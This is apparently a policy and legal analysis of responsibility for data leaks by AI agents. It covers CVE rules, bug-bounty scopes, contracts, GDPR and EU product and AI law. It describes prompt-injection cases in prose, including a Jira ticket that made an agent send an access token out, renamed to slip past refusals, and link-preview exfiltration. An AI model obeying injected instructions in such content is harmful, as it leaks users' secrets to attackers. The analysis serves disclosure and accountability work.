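A supplier can't keep a flaw out of the catalogue by ignoring it. The supplier has the first chance to issue a number for its own product. If the flaw is public and the supplier declines or doesn't respond within 72 hours, a higher body in the programme must decide whether the vulnerability exists and, if so, have another CNA issue the number. Flaws in abandoned software also qualify, with a tag marking the software as unsupported. VulnCheck issued the record for Anthropic's retired Slack connector in roughly this way, under an earlier version of the rules, but a record doesn't oblige anyone to write a fix.

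Flaws in hosted agents are less likely to appear in the CVE list. An earlier version of the rules, MITRE's *CVE Counting Rules*, allowed numbers only for flaws in software that customers could install or control. CNAs may no longer refuse a number just because a product runs in the cloud or uses AI. But OpenAI (2025) generally doesn't issue numbers for flaws on its own servers, and never does for misconfigurations. If an agent on OpenAI's servers posted the alarm code link to Slack, OpenAI could probably decline to number the flaw on either ground. Microsoft did number EchoLeak, which it fixed entirely on its own servers. Because vendors differ, customers can't assume that a hosted agent without a CVE record has no known flaws.

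Bypassing an injection filter doesn't normally qualify for a CVE number either, because the rules exclude bypasses of inherently imperfect detection methods. A researcher who wants a CVE record therefore has a better chance by reporting the preview setting than by reporting that the model followed a stranger's instructions.

### Google's known issues and Cursor's advice

In November 2025, researchers reported several ways to steal data through Antigravity, Google's programming tool. On its page for bug hunters, Google listed data exfiltration by prompt injection through the tool's browser agent as a known issue it was working to fix (Willison, 2025), which made reports of it ineligible for a reward. Google (2023) had already ruled out rewards for problems it knew about.

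Willison (2026), in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, also quotes a researcher who had reported a leak through images in Antigravity about a week earlier. According to the researcher, Google knew of the problem and marked the report as intended behaviour. That label implies that no fix is needed, whereas a company that lists a known issue accepts that it has something to fix.

Some of Antigravity's flaws came from the code it is based on, which is from Windsurf, another programming tool that Google licensed for about $2.4 billion. Rehberger had reported vulnerabilities to Windsurf in May 2025, but his report did not protect Antigravity's users. He found the same vulnerabilities still present in Antigravity, according to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*. He didn't know why, but guessed that Google's security team had been caught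 off guard.

Google also showed users a disclaimer about the risks, according to PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*. A disclaimer leaves users responsible for keeping secrets away from the tool, which is hard for programmers whose projects contain access keys.

CyberScoop reports that Google did pay a bounty for a different injection flaw in Antigravity, which it patched on 28 February 2026 after receiving the report on 6 January. The security firm Pillar Security had found that an attacker could run code even when the user had turned on Secure Mode, a setting meant to prevent this. The attack broke a specific protection that Google had promised. A preview leak is harder to report as a broken promise, because nobody has promised that the link won't be fetched.

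Cursor, a competing programming tool, put more of the responsibility on its users. In August 2025, the security firm Zenity Labs demonstrated an attack that began with an email to a company's support desk. The email automatically became a ticket in Jira, which software teams use to track work. When a programmer asked Cursor to look at the ticket, the agent sometimes followed the ticket's instructions to find an access token and send it to an outside site. The attacker gave the token a harmless nickname because models often refuse to steal anything called a key.

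In a reply that Willison quotes, Cursor called this "a known issue" and recommended that users review each MCP server before installing it and use only those that access trusted content. Reviewing the Jira connector would not have exposed the attack, because the connector worked properly and the malicious text arrived later in a ticket. Avoiding untrusted content would have helped, but the agent could not then have read tickets that customers can write, which are a large part of what a support team needs it to read.

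### What the bug bounties cover

A company's bounty rules are only a rough guide to which flaws it considers its responsibility, because it may fix a flaw without paying for the report.

Google's bug bounty program pays for what a prompt injection achieves. SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* reported in October 2025 that prompt injections and jailbreaks don't qualify by themselves, while theft of sensitive data can earn up to $15,000. One of Google's examples of a qualifying bug is an injection that summarises someone's email and sends the summary to the attacker, according to OODA Loop's *Google’s AI bounty program pays bug hunters up to $30K*. A preview leak from one of Google's own agents would have much the same effect, but Antigravity's list of known issues shows that such a leak can go unrewarded.

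Microsoft also rates severity by effect. Its severity guide gives the highest rating, critical, to an injection that takes another user's data without any user interaction. A link preview fetched on delivery seems to meet that description. An image that loads only when the user opens a message, as in the Copilot Cowork attack, might rate lower.

For Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft normally pays nothing for injections that affect only the attacker, or for types of flaw it is already looking for broad ways to prevent. The second exclusion could cover image leaks in general, so whether Microsoft pays for one may depend on what it is working on at the time. Under its wider AI bounty, Microsoft directs researchers to report flaws in OpenAI's model to OpenAI. Dividing reports by component works well when a flaw is in a single component, but a researcher who finds a preview leak may not know which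 component is at fault.

OpenAI covers agents most directly. In March 2026, it opened a separate programme for safety problems that don't meet its definition of a security vulnerability (OpenAI, 2026). The programme accepts injections that make a victim's agent leak sensitive data, if the attack works at least half the time. It also accepts flaws in connectors and pays up to $7,500, according to SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Launches Bug Bounty Program for Abuse and Safety Risks*. *OpenAI Expands AI Security Testing and Raises Bug Bounties* (Ticong, 2026) reported in November that OpenAI's top reward for security flaws had risen to nearly $172,000.

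The 50% threshold means OpenAI's staff don't have to investigate attacks they can't reproduce, but it also excludes an attack that works 10% of the time, which is enough for an attacker who can try many companies. A researcher could get around this by reporting the link preview separately, since it works almost every time once the agent has written the link. OpenAI would then have to decide whether a Slack preview is a flaw in its product.

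Researchers who test connectors for OpenAI must also follow other companies' terms. Someone who tests an OpenAI agent in Slack must therefore follow both OpenAI's and Slack's rules, even if only OpenAI pays them.

Anthropic's bug bounty policy of 7 May 2026 covers its infrastructure and code but excludes problems with what its models write. The exclusion names jailbreaks, harmful content and hallucinations but not prompt injection, so it's unclear whether the bounty covers a data leak through a link preview. Anthropic might treat the link as model content, which is excluded, or treat a connector that leaves previews on as faulty code, which is covered. Rehberger reports that Anthropic doesn't consider a related problem, its models following instructions in invisible characters, to be a vulnerability.

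Two of Anthropic's smaller rewards fit a preview leak fairly well. It may pay $100 for a report that leads only to a warning in its documentation, and $100 for a flaw that another company fixes with Anthropic coordinating. The second might apply if Slack fixed the leak by changing its default.

Anthropic's *Responsible Disclosure Policy* excludes systems that other companies run and directs researchers to those companies' own procedures. Anthropic also asks researchers not to tell a third party about a flaw until Anthropic confirms in writing that they may, though they may report "similar vulnerabilities" in other companies' services. This leaves a researcher who finds a flaw in the combination of Slack and a connector unsure whether to tell Slack straight away, because the problems in Slack and the connector are two parts of the same flaw rather than similar flaws.

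OpenClaw has the clearest rule. Its *Security trust model* lists reports that consist only of a prompt injection, with no bypass of a policy, login or sandbox, among those it closes without action. The preview leak on Telegram bypasses none of these, so OpenClaw would probably close a report of it. OpenClaw reasons that owners should assume the model can be manipulated and limit the damage by restricting who can message the agent and what it can do. That is sound advice, but an owner who follows it by letting the agent do nothing except reply on Telegram would still have previews on.

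| Company | What qualifies | What doesn't | Likely outcome for a preview leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | Theft of sensitive data from its AI products | Injection by itself; known issues | Pays if the flaw is new and the agent is Google's |
| Microsoft | Injection that harms another user | Flaws under broad mitigation; flaws in OpenAI's model | Pays if it isn't already working on that kind of leak |
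| OpenAI | Injection that leaks data at least half the time | Jailbreaks | Unclear if the failure is in another company's app |
| Anthropic | Flaws in infrastructure and code | Model content | Unclear; perhaps $100 if another company fixes it |
| OpenClaw | Ways around a policy, login or sandbox | Injection alone | Closed without action |

Companies also receive a large number of reports, which gives them a reason to keep their rules narrow. In October 2026, Google temporarily stopped accepting reports of product vulnerabilities through its open-source reward programme after a sharp rise in automated submissions, many of them invalid, according to *Google praised AI for finding bugs. Now it has too many reports* (Keverenge, 2026). A report that depends on two companies' products takes longer to check than most and may look invalid.

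### What contracts add

Contracts generally pass responsibility to the customer. OpenAI's terms of use make users responsible for what they enter and for what the model returns. Platforms' developer terms typically make the developer responsible for the app and supply the platform's interface without a warranty. A developer whose app uses OpenAI's model and posts to Slack may therefore have little recourse against either company, and can pass the risk on to its own customers through its own contracts.

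Anthropic takes this approach in its bounty policy to a problem very like a preview leak. Claude Code has a mode in which it edits files without asking, and other software on the computer may then run those files. Anthropic calls this "the responsibility of the user that enables auto-accept-edits mode". That user did at least choose the mode, whereas the office manager never chose link previews.

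A contract binds only the parties to it. The office manager's company has a contract with Slack and perhaps one with the agent's builder, but an employee whose data leaks usually has one with neither. A company that downloads a free connector has only an open-source licence, which normally disclaims all warranties. Even a paying customer's contract often caps damages, commonly at about a year's fees.

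A large customer can negotiate better contract terms, such as a promise that the agent's messages will trigger no automatic fetches. This would be more useful than a general promise of reasonable security, because the customer could test it with a server log instead of arguing about what was reasonable.

### Data protection law

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to personal data, meaning information about an identifiable person. The code `HERON-4417` opens a warehouse and identifies nobody, so its loss would probably fall outside the GDPR. That changes if the link also contains the name of a night guard who is off sick.

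The GDPR gives duties to controllers, who decide why and how to use personal data, and to processors, who handle it on a controller's behalf. The guard's employer is a controller. Slack is ordinarily a processor for the messages in a customer's workspace, and so is a builder that runs the agent on its own servers. Article 32 requires both controllers and processors to take security measures appropriate to the risk, considering the state of the art and the cost. Like the search for the cheapest cost avoider, this requirement makes it hard to excuse omitting an inexpensive precaution such as turning previews off.

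Under Article 82, a person who suffers damage from a breach of the GDPR can claim compensation, including for distress. A controller involved in the processing is liable unless it proves that it was in no way responsible for the event that caused the damage. A processor is liable only if it broke a duty that the GDPR places on processors or ignored the controller's lawful instructions. If several of them are liable for the same damage, the victim can claim the full amount from any one of them, and that one can then recover the others' shares. If the builder and Slack are both liable, the guard therefore doesn't have to work out which was more at fault.

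The EU's Court of Justice clarified these rules in December 2023, after hackers stole data from the Bulgarian tax authority. A successful attack doesn't by itself prove that security was inadequate, but the controller has to prove that it was appropriate and can't escape liability merely because hackers caused the damage. An employer whose agent leaked the guard's sick leave would therefore have to justify leaving previews on. The court also accepted that a well-founded fear of misuse can count as damage.

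An earlier judgment, *Fashion ID* (2019), also concerned an automatic request. An online clothing shop had put Facebook's "Like" button on its site, which made visitors' browsers send data to Facebook even if the visitors didn't click it. The court held that the shop was jointly responsible with Facebook for collecting and sending the data, but not for what Facebook did with it afterwards. One could argue that whoever connects an agent to an app with previews likewise shares responsibility for the resulting requests. The comparison is imperfect because the shop wanted the publicity the button brought, whereas only the attacker wants the brochure's link fetched.

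Under the GDPR, someone who only writes software, and never handles the data that passes through it, is normally neither a controller nor a processor. The regulation's preamble encourages such producers to consider data protection when they design products, but doesn't require them to. The author of a free connector that runs on a customer's computer would therefore usually owe the guard nothing under the GDPR, even if the connector's default setting caused the leak.

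### Product liability

The new EU Product Liability Directive (2024/2853) treats software as a product, including software that runs in the cloud, and makes manufacturers liable for defects whether or not they were careless. EU countries have until 9 December 2026 to put it into national law, and it covers products placed on the market after that date. Free and open-source software supplied outside a commercial activity is exempt, but a company that builds such software into a commercial product can be liable for defects in that product.

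Under the directive, a court judging whether a product is defective must consider the reasonably foreseeable effect of other products likely to be used with it. This could count against a connector's maker, who can foresee Slack's previews, and against Slack, which can now foresee agents and advises developers about them. If both products were defective and caused the same damage, each maker would be liable to the victim for all of it, even if a third party also helped cause it.

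However, none of this would lead to compensation for most preview leaks. The directive covers death and injury, including medically recognised psychological harm, as well as damage to property and the destruction or corruption of data. It excludes data used for professional purposes and property used exclusively for those purposes. A leak copies data without destroying or corrupting it, and according to the directive's preamble, an invasion of privacy or a purely financial loss doesn't trigger liability by itself. Only natural persons can claim, so the office manager's company couldn't recover the cost of changing its alarm code.

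The result could be different if a burglar used the leaked code and injured the guard. The directive covers that kind of damage, so the guard could sue the agent's maker or Slack, but would still have to prove that a product was defective and that the defect caused the injury. The company would still bear the loss of any stolen stock.

### Duties before anything goes wrong

The EU's Cyber Resilience Act sets security requirements for software and connected devices sold in the EU. Most of them apply from 11 December 2027. Manufacturers will have to supply products with a secure default configuration, check the components they build in, and handle vulnerabilities for a support period that is normally at least five years. A commercial connector that left previews on by default would be hard to defend under the secure-configuration requirement, and its maker could not simply archive it after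 a few months. Products already on the market by that date are exempt from these requirements unless their makers substantially modify them.

The Act applies to a cloud service only if it is part of a product, such as when the manufacturer designed the service and the product couldn't perform one of its functions without it. Slack's preview servers might qualify as part of its desktop and phone apps, because showing previews is one of the apps' functions. But a regulator might consider previews part of a separate online service.

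Reporting duties began earlier, on 11 September 2026, and also cover older products. A manufacturer that learns attackers are actively exploiting a vulnerability in its product must send an early warning to the authorities within 24 hours and a fuller notification within 72. A researcher's demonstration doesn't count as active exploitation, so, going by the published accounts, the leaks from Anthropic's connector, OpenClaw and Copilot Cowork would not have triggered this duty.

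A manufacturer that finds a vulnerability in a component must also tell whoever makes or maintains the component. This comes close to requiring the builder and the platform to talk to each other, but Slack probably isn't a component of a connector that sends it messages, because the connector contains none of Slack's software.

The EU's AI Act comes closer to requiring an explicit agreement, but for a narrower range of products. Article 25 requires the provider of a high-risk AI system and the suppliers of its tools, services and components to agree in writing what information and technical help the suppliers will give. Suppliers of free and open-source components are exempt, unless they supply a general-purpose model. High-risk uses include screening job applicants and assessing people's credit. An agent that summarises brochures would not normally be high-risk, so the delay to these duties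 that the European Commission proposed in November 2025 would not affect it.

Since August 2025, makers of general-purpose models have had to give companies that build on their models information about the models' capabilities and limitations. This could help those companies learn how vulnerable a model is to prompt injection. Slack would not receive this information when it only displays another company's agent, because it isn't building the model into a product.

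The Act also requires providers of systems that generate text to mark the output in a machine-readable form, with some exceptions. A platform could use such a mark to decide when to skip previews. But the rule is meant to let people detect artificial content, and it doesn't require a platform to change how it handles a marked message.

### Who owes what after one leak

Suppose the office manager works in the EU, and the brochure's link made Slack's robot visit an example.com address containing the alarm code and the guard's sick leave. The builder runs the agent commercially on its own servers.

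The employer has the most urgent duties. Once it knows of the leak, it has 72 hours to notify the data protection authority, unless the leak is unlikely to put anyone at risk. Health information has special protection under the GDPR, so the employer may well have to tell the guard too. The builder and Slack, as processors, must tell the employer without undue delay if they learn of the leak. They may never notice it, because Slack's logs would record an ordinary preview and the builder's would record a successful reply.

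The guard could then claim from the employer for any distress, and perhaps from the builder or Slack. The hardest question would be whether Slack's security was inadequate. Slack could argue that it had documented previews, provided a way to turn them off and warned developers to use it. The guard's lawyer could reply that Slack knew about the danger and still left previews on by default. The GDPR requires appropriate security but doesn't settle which side is right.

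| Party | What it would owe | Where the duty runs out |
|---|---|---|
| Employer | Notification to the authority and perhaps the guard; compensation to the guard if its security was inadequate | It bears the cost of the lost alarm code unless a contract or national law lets it recover |
| Builder that hosts the agent | Appropriate security for the guard's data; notice to the employer; whatever its contract promises | A cap on damages may leave the employer with most of its loss |
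| Slack | Appropriate security for the guard's data; notice to the employer; whatever its contract promises | No EU rule specifically requires it to stop fetching links from agents |
| Author of a free, non-commercial connector | Normally nothing under these EU laws | A licence usually disclaims liability as well |

The same request leaked two secrets, but the law treats them differently. The guard has a right to compensation regardless of any contract, and several companies may have to pay it. For the alarm code, the employer would have to rely on its contracts with Slack and the builder, or persuade a national court that one of them had been negligent. If the employer had used the free connector instead, it might have been able to claim only from the attacker.
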